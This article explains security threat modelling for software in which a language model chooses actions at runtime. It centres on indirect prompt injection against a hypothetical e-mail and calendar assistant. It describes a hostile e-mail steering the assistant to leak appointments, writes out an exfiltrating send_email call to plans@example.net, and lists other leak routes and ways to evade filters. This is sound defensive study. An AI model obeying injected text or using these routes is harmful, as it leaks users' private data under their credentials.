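# Security threat modelling for software whose actions a language model chooses at runtime

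## Software in which a language model chooses the next step

In threat modelling, engineers work out who might want to harm a system, how they could reach it and what damage would follow. Threat modelling, input validation, auditing and failure analysis were all developed for programs whose every possible step a developer had written beforehand. In an agent, a language model (a system trained to continue text) repeatedly chooses the next action, and ordinary code carries it out. Text from outside the program can therefore change what it does even when the code contains no bug.

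The word "agent" is also used more loosely. *Fully Autonomous AI Agents Should Not be Developed* (Mitchell, Ghosh and colleagues, 2025) found it applied to everything from single-step prompt-and-response systems to multi-step customer support. Anthropic's developer guide, *Building effective agents*, uses it only for systems in which the model directs its own process, and uses "workflow" for those in which models run inside code paths that a developer fixed in advance.

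### From written branches to a loop

A conventional program that handles meeting invitations might accept if the slot is free and decline otherwise. Its control flow, meaning the order in which its steps run and the choices that determine that order, is in the source code, where a reviewer can read both branches. An invitation may contain any text, but unless the code has a bug, the program only copies that text into a description field.

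An agent's source code contains a loop and a list of tools. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes the loop inside Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. The harness, which is the ordinary code around the model, first assembles the context, which is all the text the model receives at that step. For Codex, this includes developer instructions, the available tools with the arguments each accepts, a description of the working environment and the user's message. The model returns either a message to the user or a tool call, which is a structured request for the harness to run a named function with given arguments. In Bolin's example, the function is a command shell and the argument is a command that prints a README file. The harness runs the command, appends both the call and its output to the context, and queries the model again. The loop ends when the model returns a message with no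 tool call, by which point the model may have made hundreds of calls.

Codex sends the whole history again on every pass, so the earlier context forms an exact prefix of the later one. A sentence that entered at the third step is still there at the thirtieth, unless the harness has since compacted the conversation into something shorter. Each item also carries a role (system, developer, user or assistant, in falling order of priority) that indicates how much weight the model should give it. However, David C points out in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post from the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, that current models enforce no boundary between instructions and data inside a prompt. They predict the next token, a word or fragment of a word, from all the tokens so far, including those in the README.

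### How much the model controls

Mitchell and colleagues rank systems on five levels by how far a model determines program flow. At the lowest level the program prints the model's answer, and at the highest it executes code the model has just written. A security analyst can capture much of the difference with three degrees of control, because at each successive degree the analyst can list less of what the software might do before it runs.

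At the lowest degree of control, the model only fills in a value. For example, a mail program might use a model to write a one-line summary of each message and display it above the message. The analyst can list every path through this program and every place the summary goes, so only the summary's content is unknown. A sender could still word a message so that the model produces a false summary of it, but the harm is limited to one field on the screen.

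A model can also pick among fixed branches. Anthropic's example is a customer-service system that sorts queries into general questions, refund requests and technical support, each with its own downstream process. An analyst can list the branches and work out the worst outcome of each, but cannot predict which branch a given message will trigger. A deceptive message can at most trigger a branch that a developer wrote.

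When the model composes an open sequence of calls, it selects the tools, their arguments, their order and when to stop. An analyst can still list the action space, which *Risks and Controls for Multi-Agent Systems* (2026) defines as the tools, permissions and systems within the agent's reach, but there are too many possible sequences to list. Four tools allow 4ⁿ sequences of n calls, or 1,048,576 for ten calls, even without counting different arguments. Sequeira and Iqbal (2026), in *Agent-Sentry*, note that the execution flow is not known beforehand even for a request as simple as summarising recent e-mails. They add that most deployed agents serve a narrow purpose, so their legitimate runs resemble one another, and forwarding a message then immediately deleting it would stand out. This regularity is less useful to an analyst who needs to know what an agent could do, because it describes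 what the agent usually does.

Anthropic recommends agents for problems where developers can't predict the number of steps or hardcode a path. Choosing steps at runtime makes an agent useful to customers with these problems, but it also prevents an analyst from listing the steps in advance.

### An e-mail and calendar assistant

For example, a hypothetical assistant works for one user, holds a credential for that user's mailbox and calendar, and has four tools. Its harness runs every well-formed tool call without asking the user to confirm.

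| Tool | What it can do | Who can write the text involved |
|---|---|---|
| read_email | Return any message in the mailbox | Anyone who knows the user's address |
| list_events | Return calendar entries with titles and notes | The user, and anyone who can send an invitation |
| update_event | Change the time, title, notes or guests of an entry | The model writes the arguments; the calendar service returns a status |
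| send_email | Send a message in the user's name to any address | The model writes the arguments; the mail service returns a status |

The rest of the context is the developer's instructions and the user's request. Content is untrusted if anyone other than the developer or the user could have written or altered it, and here it enters through read_email and list_events. Sequeira and Iqbal classify an e-mail agent's tools in a similar way: reading contacts or drafts is trusted retrieval, reading e-mails or attachments is untrusted retrieval, and sending or deleting is an action. By their rule, list_events is untrusted retrieval, because a stranger can add text to the calendar by sending an invitation.

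Suppose the user tells the assistant that Priya has proposed a new time for Thursday's meeting, and asks it to move the meeting and let her know. The model calls read_email and gets the recent messages, including one from Priya that suggests Friday at ten. It then calls list_events for Thursday to find the meeting, update_event to move it, and send_email to confirm with Priya. No developer specified that order. The new time came from Priya's message, so an assistant that ignored the contents of e-mail could not do the job.

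Now suppose the user makes the same request when her recent mail also includes a message from a stranger. Part of that message tells any assistant processing the mailbox to collect the coming week's appointments and send them to an outside address. The call to read_email returns this message together with Priya's. If the model follows the stranger's instructions, it next calls list_events, as in the earlier run, but for the whole week instead of Thursday, and then calls send_email to send the appointments to the stranger. It may then also move the meeting, so that the user sees the result she asked for.

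When a model wrongly treats data as instructions, the result can be theft of the user's data or unintended actions under the user's credentials (Microsoft, 2025). In the second run, the mail service received a valid credential and the harness received valid arguments. This is misdirection, a harmful outcome in which every component works as its makers built it to, but for the wrong party or purpose.

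### Threat models, diagrams and boundaries

A threat model describes what is worth protecting (the assets), who might attack it (the adversary), where they can get something into the system (the entry points) and what damage could result (the harms). For the assistant, the assets are the contents of the mailbox and calendar and the user's ability to write in her own name. The adversary can send her an e-mail or an invitation but has no password. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) describes such an adversary as one who "controls content, not code". The entry points are the two reading tools, and the harms include leaked appointments, messages the user never meant to send and meetings moved without her knowledge.

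Engineers usually work from a data-flow diagram, a drawing of the people, programs and data stores in a system, with arrows for the data that passes between them. Across some arrows they draw a line called a trust boundary, which marks where data or requests pass between parties with different trust or privileges. *Local LLM Agents as Vulnerable Runtimes* (2026) adapts this idea to agents by placing a boundary wherever a class of untrusted data meets a class of privileged operation. Each boundary comes with a yes-or-no question, such as whether a text is safe to place among trusted instructions.

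There is less agreement on whether the model belongs inside the trusted base. Mellafe Zuvic puts the harness and the tools inside and leaves the model outside, as an untrusted parser of text. Sequeira and Iqbal count the model among the trustworthy parts but allow that retrieved content may compromise it during a run. *SoK* (2026), a survey of attacks on agents, puts the model's weights (the numbers that training produced) inside the trusted base but treats the model's output as untrusted code that needs checking before it runs. The three positions have the same consequence for the stranger's e-mail, because under each of them a tool call from the model does not prove that the user wanted it. They differ if someone corrupted the model before deployment. Mellafe Zuvic's boundary still applies in that case, because a hidden backdoor and a hostile e-mail both show up as a proposed tool call,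 whereas the other two positions assume that the weights are sound.

### The confused deputy

The assistant used its own permission to read the calendar for a stranger who had none. A confused deputy is a program that has some authority and is induced to use it by someone who lacks that authority. The term comes from Hardy (1988). *The Confused Deputy* describes events of about 1977 at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Its compiler collected statistics on the language features people used. To let it save them, the staff gave it permission to write files in its own directory, which also held the company's billing file. Users could name a file to receive debugging output, and one of them named the billing file. The operating system allowed the write because the compiler had permission, and the output destroyed the billing data.

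Hardy could not find a faulty line of code. The code that wrote the debugging output was correct when its author wrote it, and became wrong when someone added the licence. He concluded that the compiler ran with authority from two sources, its own and that of the user who invoked it, and had no way to specify which one to use for a given file. He favoured using capabilities, each of which is a single object that identifies a file and carries permission to use it. The user would then have had to give the compiler permission to write to the billing file, which he did not have.

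The assistant fits this pattern, but the problem is worse because the writer of a hostile e-mail can influence which step comes next. Tymshare's user only supplied one argument to a step the compiler was going to perform anyway. David C adds that engineers can repair a classical confused deputy, but can only lower the risk and limit the damage with a language model, which he considers "inherently confusable".

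Mellafe Zuvic read the public source code of three common packages for building agents, LangChain/LangGraph, LlamaIndex and the Stripe Agent Toolkit, to see what happens between the model's tool call and its execution. All three restrict which tools the model can reach, but by default none checks whether the model has authority to use the specific values in a call. A payment to an attacker's account therefore goes through as long as the account number is well formed. He does not claim that the products themselves are vulnerable, since developers can add the check, but he stresses that they have to know it is missing.

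### Where prompt injection comes from

Prompt injection is text that makes a model follow the instructions of the text's author instead of those of the user or developer. On 11 September 2022 Riley Goodside posted examples in which GPT-3, an early OpenAI model, was given a passage to translate into French and obeyed an order contained in the passage. The next day Willison (2022), in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3*, proposed the name and explained that this was a security problem because developers were building products by joining their own instructions and a user's text into one string. He compared it to SQL injection, an older attack on database queries assembled the same way, and hoped for an interface that would take instructions and data separately. Four days later Willison (2022), in *I don't know how to solve prompt injection*, wrote that he knew how to beat SQL injection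 and many other exploits but had no idea how to beat this one reliably. By April 2023 he had added a note to the first post saying that separating instructions from data was extremely difficult, if not impossible, with current model architectures.

In those first cases the attacker typed directly into the system, and the result was mostly embarrassment. A recruitment startup's Twitter bot, released that same week, was soon repeating whatever strangers told it to. In *Not what you've signed up for*, Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023) described indirect prompt injection, in which the attacker places the text in material that the agent will read during its work, such as a web page or an e-mail. The victim is a user who asked for something harmless. They demonstrated the attack against Bing Chat, which then ran on GPT-4, and against mock applications they built. One of these closely resembled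 the invented assistant. It read an incoming message, looked through the user's address book and forwarded the message to the contacts in it, whose own assistants could then do the same.

Greshake and colleagues used prepared content in the mock applications. They showed that such attacks are possible but did not measure how often they succeed. Their more lasting contribution is the observation that, because the model controls when and how other functions are called, whoever steers the model also steers those calls.

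### What four security practices take for granted

Threat modelling relies on knowing the paths data can take. An engineer goes through the arrows of a data-flow diagram and asks what could go wrong along each, which works when the code fixes how the arrows connect. The assistant's diagram has an arrow from read_email to the model and another from the model to send_email, but whether data flows from one to the other in a given run depends on the emails the model reads. Microsoft says more generally that because AI systems are nondeterministic, analysts have to reason about ranges of behaviour, including rare but severe failures, rather than single outcomes.

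Input validation traditionally assumes that input follows a known grammar, so a date field can reject anything that isn't a date. Checking grammar can't distinguish a request to move a meeting from a request to disclose a calendar, because both are valid English. Disclosing the calendar may also be appropriate, such as when the recipient is the user's own secretary.

Auditors rely on repeatable behaviour. They can rerun an ordinary program on its recorded inputs and watch it take the same path. An agent may take a different path on a second run, because agents commonly sample the model's output from a range of likely continuations. The record also may not show why the agent acted as it did. *Ghost in the Agent* (2026) describes untrusted text that works as a condition, for instance by making a tool call depend on whether an e-mail contains a certain word. Such text changes what the agent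 does without appearing in the call.

Investigators analysing a failure look for a part that broke, but those investigating the leaked calendar would have to explain the loss without one. The mail service delivered a message, the harness executed valid calls, and the model followed an instruction in its context.

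## What input validation can and cannot do

Input validation means checking data before a program acts on it. Validation and a related technique, the parameterised query, have largely solved SQL injection, the attack Willison compared prompt injection to when he coined the latter term. Neither technique works for the text a language model reads, mostly because of how databases and models work. Validation is still useful for checking the model's output.

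### Why a database can keep commands and data apart

SQL is the language in which programs query most databases. Its grammar separates commands from values, and text values stand between quotation marks. Suppose a calendar service needs to find every meeting that a given person organised. A careless programmer might build the query by joining strings:

```
query = "SELECT title, start FROM events WHERE organiser = '" + name + "'"
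```

This works for the name Khan, but the apostrophe in O'Brien closes the quoted value early, so the database tries to parse the remaining letters as SQL and reports an error. An attacker would follow the apostrophe with text that forms a valid command.

A parameterised query avoids the problem:

```
query = "SELECT title, start FROM events WHERE organiser = ?"
database.execute(query, [name])
```

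The database parses the first line with the question mark as an empty slot, which fixes what the command will do. The name fills the slot separately and is never parsed, so it can contain apostrophes or even a complete SQL command and will still only be compared with other names. A slot can hold a value but not part of the command, so if users can also choose the sort column, the programmer has to check their choice against a list of permitted columns.

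A parameterised query works even if the programmer doesn't recognise an attack. It meets all three conditions that Bhattarai and Vu (2026), in *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries*, set for separating commands from data. First, something other than an input's content, such as the channel it arrived through, must determine whether it is a command or data. Second, the system must be able to check that classification before it executes anything. Third, no input classed as data may trigger an operation reserved for commands.

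### The argument from the next token

David C argues that these conditions cannot apply to a language model. A SQL database engine executes instructions, and it stores data or uses it in queries. A language model has no separate operations for instructions and data because it only predicts the next token. In his example, a recruiter's software tells a model to score a CV, and the candidate has hidden a sentence in the CV telling the model to approve it. The model receives both sentences as tokens in one sequence.

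Developers can try to detect injected instructions, train models to give priority to the real ones, or mark which part of the prompt is data. David C objects that each of these methods imposes a distinction between instructions and data on a technology that does not inherently have one. He therefore prefers the label "inherently confusable deputy" to the comparison with code injection, and adds that a system that cannot tolerate the remaining risk may be a poor use for a model. He sees "a good chance" that prompt injection will never have a fix as complete as parameterised queries are for SQL injection.

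The caution is justified, because the argument shows only that current models enforce no boundary between instructions and data, not that a model couldn't learn one or that engineers couldn't build one. *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models* (Pant, Lohani and Kumar, 2026) compares these models to computer memory, which also has no inherent distinction between instructions and data because both are bytes. Attackers long exploited this ambiguity through buffer overflows, in which overlong input spills into memory that the processor later executes. In 2003 the chip maker AMD introduced a bit that marks regions of memory as non-executable. Writing different bytes to a region doesn't change the mark, because the mark is separate from the bytes.

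Next-token prediction also describes only what a model outputs, and a model could learn to treat quoted mail differently from a request in order to predict well. *Can LLMs Separate Instructions From Data?* (2024) proposes measuring this by placing a short, unrelated instruction first in the part of the input meant for instructions, then in the part meant for data, and comparing the model's responses. A model that joined the two parts together would have a separation score of zero. Real models should score between that and perfect separation, but none of those tested separated the two reliably. One reason may be that models infer who is speaking more from the style of a text than from its role label, as Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell found in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (2026).

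### Building the boundary into the model

*A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) describes the goal as a model that can take information from untrusted content without letting that content change goals, permissions or tool policies. According to the survey, delimiters and role labels help but are not a hard boundary.

*ASIDE* (Zverev, Kortukov and colleagues, 2025) builds the distinction between instructions and data into the model. A model first converts each token into an embedding, a list of numbers that represents the token in all later computation. Normally the word "send" has the same embedding in a user's request as in a stranger's e-mail, so the model has to infer its role from the surrounding text. ASIDE leaves the embeddings of instructions unchanged and rotates those of data by 90 degrees, taking the numbers in pairs and turning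 each pair (x, y) into (−y, x). The software around the model selects which tokens to rotate according to where they came from, so a stranger cannot undo the rotation by typing a delimiter into an e-mail.

The researchers applied ASIDE, which rotates the embeddings of data, to six models with 7 to 13 billion parameters and fine-tuned them on about 52,000 ordinary instruction-following examples, none of which were attacks. For comparison, they trained the same models with delimiters and a prompt that explained which part was data. ASIDE raised the separation score by 12.3 to 44.1 percentage points. The average success rate of attacks fell from 14.7% to 4.9% on one set of indirect injections, but only from 45% to 36% on another, where the rate rose for one of the six models. When the researchers gave injected text the embeddings of instructions again, the model obeyed it almost twice as often,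 which is good evidence that the rotation caused the improvement.

These were fixed attacks on single exchanges, whereas an agent's context may hold dozens of tool results. A more basic problem is that the model still has to learn what the rotation means. Judged by Bhattarai and Vu's conditions, ASIDE has a label that an attacker cannot forge and the software can check in advance, but text labelled as data can still sometimes steer the output.

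Pant and colleagues try to prove that training alone can never guarantee a boundary. The property they want is that two inputs with the same meaning always lead to the same decisions about tools, refusals and memory, however someone has encoded them. The proof starts from how well anyone could tell trusted from untrusted text by looking at the model's internal representations. If both kinds are equally common, the lowest possible error rate is

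error = ½ × (1 − TV)

where TV, the total variation distance, is 0 if the two kinds of text produce identical distributions of representations and 1 if those distributions do not overlap at all. A distance of 0.9 would leave an error of 5%. The distributions certainly overlap at the first layer of an ordinary model, because words such as "the" and "you" occur in both kinds of text and have one embedding each. In deeper layers, where a token's representation also reflects its context, the paper assumes that they overlap. Its measurements on one small model show the two kinds of text moving apart in the early layers and partly back together in the later ones, but samples can lie close together without their distributions overlapping.

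The other half of the proof is that a text can be reworded and re-encoded in endless ways, while training covers a finite number of them, so good behaviour on the training examples cannot guarantee good behaviour on the rest. The proof does not predict how often models will fail. In the paper's small test, two models refused the injected requests under all five attack techniques.

The result does not cover models that process instructions and data in separate encoders, models whose internal connections stop untrusted text from influencing control decisions, or systems in which outside software authorises tool calls. Pant and colleagues count ASIDE among the exceptions, which seems generous because its rotated tokens still enter the same computation as the instructions.

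### Recognising hostile text

Developers who cannot separate instructions from data may try to find hostile text and remove it. The simplest filter is a deny-list, which blocks messages containing known bad phrases. David C warns against relying on deny-lists because there are infinitely many ways to rephrase an attack. An eight-word sentence with five interchangeable choices for each word has 5⁸, or 390,625, versions. An attacker can also translate the text, rewrite it in base64 (which encodes any data as ordinary characters) or replace some letters with Unicode characters that look the same. The result no longer matches anything on the list, but a capable model can often still read it.

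Images can also bypass a text filter. Bhattarai and Vu describe a user who uploads a picture of a forbidden request with an innocent covering message. The filter receives only the message, but the model reads the picture. A scanned email attachment would bypass the filter in the same way. Deny-lists also block legitimate mail, because people often ask colleagues to ignore a previous message.

A better filter would judge what a text means, usually by asking another language model. Glukhov, Shumailov and colleagues argue in *LLM Censorship* (2023) that such filters have limits that better models will not remove. They start from Rice's theorem, which implies that no algorithm can decide for every program whether its behaviour has a given property, unless all programs have that property or none do. A filter that must judge what a program or a set of programmatic instructions will do faces the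 same problem. They concede that the theorem does not strictly apply to real systems, whose inputs and memory are finite, but deciding whether a program is malware is also hard in practice.

The next argument applies to finite texts. A forbidden text remains just as harmful after encryption if the recipient can decrypt it, so a consistent filter should also block the encrypted version. But any innocent-looking output could stand for a forbidden one under some code. A filter that does not know which codes the recipient has must therefore permit everything or nothing. The argument requires a model that can apply the code accurately, and it does not cover filters that examine input and output together or inspect the model's internal state.

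The most important point for agents, made in *Position* (Glukhov et al., 2024), is that parts that each pass a filter can combine into something harmful. A user can ask for the components of a malicious program in separate conversations. Each component has ordinary uses and passes the filter, and the user then assembles them. The user has to know how the parts fit together, but a system with tools may do the assembling itself. For the e-mail and calendar assistant, listing next week's events is harmless and so is sending an e-mail, but a filter that checks each call separately may well approve the pair that leaks the calendar.

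Glukhov and colleagues show that a user could extract any text from a sufficiently capable model even if a filter permitted only two answers. The model would spell out the text one bit at a time, using one answer for 0 and the other for 1. Suppose a restricted version of the assistant could only answer "free" or "busy" when someone proposed a meeting. A stranger who proposed every half-hour slot from nine to five, Monday to Friday, would learn from the 80 answers when the user was busy that week, and a filter would have no reason to block any of those answers.

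In *On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment*, Ball, Gluch and colleagues (2025) consider filters that use less computation than the model they protect, as most practical filters do. Their proof uses time-lock puzzles, which encrypt a message so that nobody can read it without a set amount of computation. A large model could do that computation and follow the hidden request, while a much faster filter could not distinguish the prompt from an innocent one. The proof shows that for some models, every fast filter fails. Ball, Gluch and colleagues acknowledge that the model in their proof behaves in a contrived way, so it remains an open question how well filters protect the models people use.

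A filter that searches each of a model's answers for a secret could miss a leak, because the secret need not appear in any of them. *Inadvertent Context Leakage in Language Models* (2026) reports that a model's harmless outputs carry some information about a secret in its context, even when the model correctly refuses to reveal it. An adversary trained by reinforcement learning used this information to extract complete US Social Security numbers from realistic agents running on Claude Opus 4.6 and Gemini 3.1 Pro.

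### False alarms when attacks are rare

Even an accurate detector can be hard to use if hostile documents are rare. Suppose 1 document in 10,000 is hostile, and a detector catches 99% of hostile documents and raises a false alarm on 1% of harmless ones. These figures are invented to show the arithmetic. In a million documents, the results would be:

| | Alarm | No alarm | Total |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
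| Hostile | 99 | 1 | 100 |
| Harmless | 9,999 | 989,901 | 999,900 |
| Total | 10,098 | 989,902 | 1,000,000 |

Only 99 of the 10,098 alarms, about 1%, are real. A user who receives 100 messages a day would see roughly one false alarm a day and one hostile message every hundred days. If the assistant asked her about each alarm, she would dismiss about a hundred before a real one, and would probably have stopped reading them by then. If it deleted flagged messages instead, she would lose about one legitimate message a day.

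The harness could respond to an alarm less drastically, such as by disabling send_email for the rest of the run. But if the errors are independent, a run that reads 20 harmless messages has about an 18% chance of at least one false alarm, so the assistant would often be unable to confirm a meeting.

The share of alarms that are real depends heavily on how common attacks are. If 1 document in 100 were hostile, half of the same detector's alarms would be real. If 1 in 10,000 were hostile, the detector would need a false-alarm rate of about 0.01%, a hundred times lower, for half its alarms to be real.

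The 99% catch rate is also less reassuring than it looks, because attackers can try again. If each new wording had an independent 1% chance of getting through, an attacker with 100 attempts would have a 63% chance of succeeding at least once. An attacker who could test messages on a copy of the detector would only need to send the one that passed.

### Checking what the model produces

A tool call is much easier to validate than an e-mail because the developer defined what a valid call looks like. The assistant's harness accepts four function names, each with a fixed set of arguments, and can reject anything else without interpreting English. Checking tool calls also covers every route hostile text might have taken to the model, including the scanned attachment that a text filter would miss.

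In Bhattarai and Vu's design, the model proposes an action from a finite list with typed parameters, ordinary code allows or denies it, and separate software makes the actual call. A persuasive e-mail may change what the model proposes, but it cannot change the rule in the code. Their guarantee covers only actions that the rule forbids, and they point out that a user who is allowed to send e-mail can still send a harmful one.

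The assistant could use several kinds of check, each of which leaves something through:

| Check | Example | What still passes |
|---|---|---|
| Schema | update_event must name an existing event and may change only the listed fields | Any well-formed change |
| Type and range | A meeting must end after it starts and fall within the next year | A plausible but wrong time |
| Allowlist | send_email accepts only addresses in the user's contacts | A leak to one of those contacts |
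| Amount and rate | One recipient per message and ten messages an hour | One message containing the week's appointments |
| Escaping | The calendar page displays an event title as text and never runs it as code | A misleading title |

An allowlist works better than a deny-list because it blocks whatever the developer did not think of, but it also limits what the user can do. Glukhov and colleagues observe that a model restricted to inputs and outputs its provider has approved in advance would be little more than a large lookup table. An e-mail assistant may still be able to work from a list of approved recipients, though not from a list of approved messages.

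Web addresses need an allowlist as well. If the assistant's replies can include images, the program that displays the replies may fetch each image automatically, and the address it requests can carry text to whoever runs the server. A stranger could then receive the appointments without the assistant calling send_email.

Escaping matters because the model's output often becomes another program's input. The model might copy a title from a stranger's invitation into update_event. If the calendar's web page inserts that title into its HTML without escaping it, a browser may run part of it as a script. This is an ordinary bug, and the well-known fix is to convert the special characters so that the browser displays them. A parameterised query does the same job for a database, and passing arguments as a list instead of one joined string does it for a shell. Escaping cannot help when the argument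 is meant to be a command, as with Codex's shell tool. The developer then has to limit which commands may run or what they can reach.

### When a valid argument is the wrong one

In the run where the assistant leaked the calendar, its harness would have received two calls like these:

```
send_email(to="priya@example.com", subject="Thursday's meeting", body=...)
send_email(to="plans@example.net", subject="Next week", body=...)
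```

Both calls have the right arguments and valid addresses, and two messages are well within any reasonable limit. Nothing in the second address shows that it belongs to an attacker. A developer who stopped at these checks would have about as much protection as the three agent packages that Mellafe Zuvic examined provide by default.

An allowlist of contacts would stop the second call, provided the stranger was not already on it. He or she could already be there, because some mail programs save the address of anyone the user has replied to. A rule that let the assistant answer anyone who had written to the user would be worse, because the stranger has written to her. A stricter harness could give the model a list of contact identifiers and accept only those, so that the model could choose Priya but could not enter a new address. The user would then have to type any new address herself.

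A message to the right recipient may still include information they shouldn't have. Priya needs to know that the meeting is now on Friday, but she probably shouldn't be told about the user's medical appointments. A schema for the body field would accept either, because both are text.

A message can do harm without containing any instructions. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) notes that even if a model separated instructions from data perfectly, hostile data could still do harm through tool arguments. For example, someone posing as Priya could write that Friday at eleven suits her best. The assistant would correctly treat this as information and move the meeting to a time she had never proposed. Attackers similarly got around the non-executable bit by making programs run code that was already in memory instead of supplying their own.

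The resulting call to update_event would contain a real event and a sensible time, so it would pass every check in the table. To reject it, the harness would need a record of who supplied the time and whether that person was allowed to choose it. A tool call contains that information only if the system has tracked it since the message arrived, as information-flow control does.

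## How to draw a threat model for an agent

Before a harness can track where a value came from, engineers have to decide which data flows are dangerous. They can do this with the ordinary threat-modelling procedure, which needs only a few changes for agents.

### The ordinary procedure

Dandy, in *Why threat modeling is the technique that survives AI disruption*, organises the work around four questions: what are we working on, what can go wrong, what are we going to do about it, and did we do a good job? Analysts usually answer the first with a data-flow diagram and its trust boundaries. Many answer the second with STRIDE, a list of six categories of threat that Loren Kohnfelder and Praerit Garg developed at Microsoft in the 1990s. The analyst goes through the components or boundaries one by one and asks how each category could apply. For the e-mail and calendar assistant, she might write:

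| STRIDE category | Threat to the assistant | Usual control |
|---|---|---|
| Spoofing | Someone logs in as the user | A password and a second factor |
| Tampering | Someone alters a message on its way to the mailbox | Encrypted connections |
| Repudiation | A user denies having sent a message | A log of sent mail |
| Information disclosure | Another customer reads her calendar | An access check on every request |
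| Denial of service | Someone floods the mailbox | Limits on incoming mail |
| Elevation of privilege | An ordinary user gains an administrator's rights | Separate administrator accounts |

GTKlondike's *Threat Modeling LLM Applications* applies this procedure to a generic application that contains a language model. The diagram shows outside sources of text, the model, the functions it can call, and private data, with a trust boundary between the model and each of the other three. GTKlondike identified seven vulnerabilities, including that outside text can control the model's output and that a model cannot enforce permissions on data. The paper therefore recommends treating all of the model's output as untrusted and checking permissions at the data store instead of relying on the model to check them.

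### What a review of separate components misses

*Threat modeling agentic AI* (Schneider, 2026) describes how a STRIDE review of a company's assistant can miss an attack. The reviewer finds that the mail connection checks credentials, a filter screens retrieved documents, only authorised staff can change the model's instructions, and the tools are on an allowlist, so every component passes. An attacker could still take data out through a series of permitted steps, as in EchoLeak, a vulnerability in Microsoft's Copilot.

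The leaked calendar would pass the same review. The stranger wrote under her own name, didn't alter anyone's message and didn't log in to anything. STRIDE covers the result as information disclosure, but an analyst who checks for it finds a request with a valid credential at the calendar and an ordinary outgoing message at the mail service. The analyst also needs to check whether text that arrived through read_email can determine what the agent does with the calendar and the mail service. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) points out that a valid credential may get an agent into a system without establishing which actions it may take there.

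Automated scanners have a similar blind spot. The Cloud Security Alliance, an industry body, gives the example of a line of code that passes a command to a shell. A scanner correctly flags the line as a possible command injection, but it does not report the more serious problem, which is that a model chooses the command after reading untrusted text.

Agents are also hard to place in a data-flow diagram, which gives each element one role, such as an outside actor, a process or a data store. Analysts use that role to work out which threats to consider. According to *Taking Maestro in Stride*, by the security consultancy Bishop Fox, an agent can play all of these roles at once, and an agent that one process trusts may be a hostile outsider to another. The firm reports that some organisations now start by assuming their own agents are insider threats.

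The revised procedure below keeps the diagram and the boundaries. Its five steps draw on Schneider's method of following an attack from one part of an agent to the next.

### Step 1: list everyone who can write into the context

The analyst starts by listing the people who can write into the assistant's context, because it is hard to tell from a tool's name who wrote the text it returns. These people include the developer, the user, and anyone who can send the user an e-mail or an invitation. The sender of an e-mail also chooses its subject line, attachments and display name.

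Less obvious writers include people whose words reach the mailbox indirectly. Priya's reply may quote a message from someone the user has never met. A delivery-failure notice from the mail service may repeat part of the failed message. Schneider also counts tool descriptions as entry points when they come from outside suppliers, for example through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common way to connect tools to agents.

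*SoK* describes an attacker on this list as a runtime supplier who leaves material where an agent is likely to fetch it.

### Step 2: give the model's output the lowest trust in its context

Next, the analyst ranks the writers by trust, with the developer at the top, then the user, then everyone else. She assigns each tool call the lowest rank found anywhere in the context when the model produced it:

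trust(call) = min { trust(item) : item in the context }

When the user asks the assistant to move Thursday's meeting, the context contains only her words and the developer's, so the assistant's call to read_email has the user's rank. Once read_email returns, the context may contain a stranger's message, so every later call in the run has the stranger's rank. The harness keeps adding to the same history, so the rank can fall during a run but cannot rise. Summarising the history doesn't raise the rank, because the stranger's text may have influenced the summary.

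This is a worst-case assumption and doesn't measure how often a model would obey the stranger. It also gives the legitimate confirmation to Priya the same low rank as the leaked calendar, so an analyst can't decide what to block from the rank alone. She can use the rank to find the calls that ordinary code or a person has to check, because at those points the model's choice isn't evidence of what the user wants.

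### Step 3: replace the expected path with everything the permissions allow

Developers usually diagram the path they intend: read Priya's message, find the meeting, move it, confirm. But the assistant's harness accepts calls to its four tools in any order, so the diagram should have an arrow from each source of untrusted text to each action the model can take.

The analyst only needs to know which effects can follow which sources, so she doesn't have to list every sequence of calls. The assistant has two sources of untrusted text, read_email and list_events, and three ways to affect something outside the model: update_event, send_email and the reply it shows the user. That makes six pairs of source and effect to examine. A longer sequence matters only if it makes a new effect possible, such as adding private data to what the model can send.

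For each pair, the analyst has to consider everything the tool can do, including uses nobody expects. The update_event tool is meant for moving meetings, but it can also change an event's guests. Many calendar services e-mail each new guest an invitation containing the event's title and notes. A model that copied next week's appointments into the notes and added a stranger as a guest would therefore send the stranger those appointments without calling send_email.

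### Step 4: mark stored text as an input to later sessions

*SoK* separates attacks that end when the context is cleared from attacks that persist in an agent's stored memory. The assistant has no memory feature, but text can still carry over from one session to the next through its tools. Text that the model writes into an event's notes on Monday will come back through list_events on Tuesday, and the calendar may show the user as the author. Messages the assistant has sent can return in the same way, since read_email can open anything in the mailbox.

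The analyst should draw each data store twice, once as an output of the present session and once as an input to the next. Stored text keeps the lowest trust rank of anything in the model's context when the model wrote it. Otherwise, an instruction in a stranger's e-mail could gain the user's rank if the model saved it to her calendar and read it back in a later session. Deleting the original e-mail would not remove the saved copy.

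### Step 5: trace each route to a harmful effect

Finally, the analyst takes each harm and works backwards. An attack tree is a convenient way to do this. The harm goes at the top, and beneath it are the conditions that must all hold (AND) or of which one is enough (OR). For the leaked calendar, the tree looks like this:

```
A stranger obtains next week's appointments
  AND  hostile text enters the context
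         OR  through an e-mail
         OR  through an invitation
  AND  the model follows the text
  AND  the model reads the calendar
  AND  the appointments leave
         OR  in a message from send_email
         OR  in an invitation to a new guest
         OR  in the address of an image in the reply
```

The attack has six versions, because there are two ways in and three ways out. Guarding only send_email would stop two of them, while blocking all three exits would stop all six. Preventing the assistant from reading the calendar after it has read untrusted text would also stop all six, but the assistant could then not find the meeting it has to move. The attack also requires the model to follow the untrusted text. Training can make this less likely, but a developer can't switch it off as they can the other conditions.

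Repeating the exercise for the other harms gives the assistant's threat model:

| Source | Route | Harmful effect | Control |
|---|---|---|---|
| Stranger's e-mail | read_email → list_events → send_email | The stranger receives the week's appointments | The user approves any recipient she has not named |
| Stranger's e-mail | read_email → list_events → update_event, with a new guest | The calendar service sends the appointments in an invitation | The same approval for new guests |
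| Stranger's invitation | list_events → read_email → send_email | Private messages leave the mailbox | The same approval, plus a limit on which messages a task may open |
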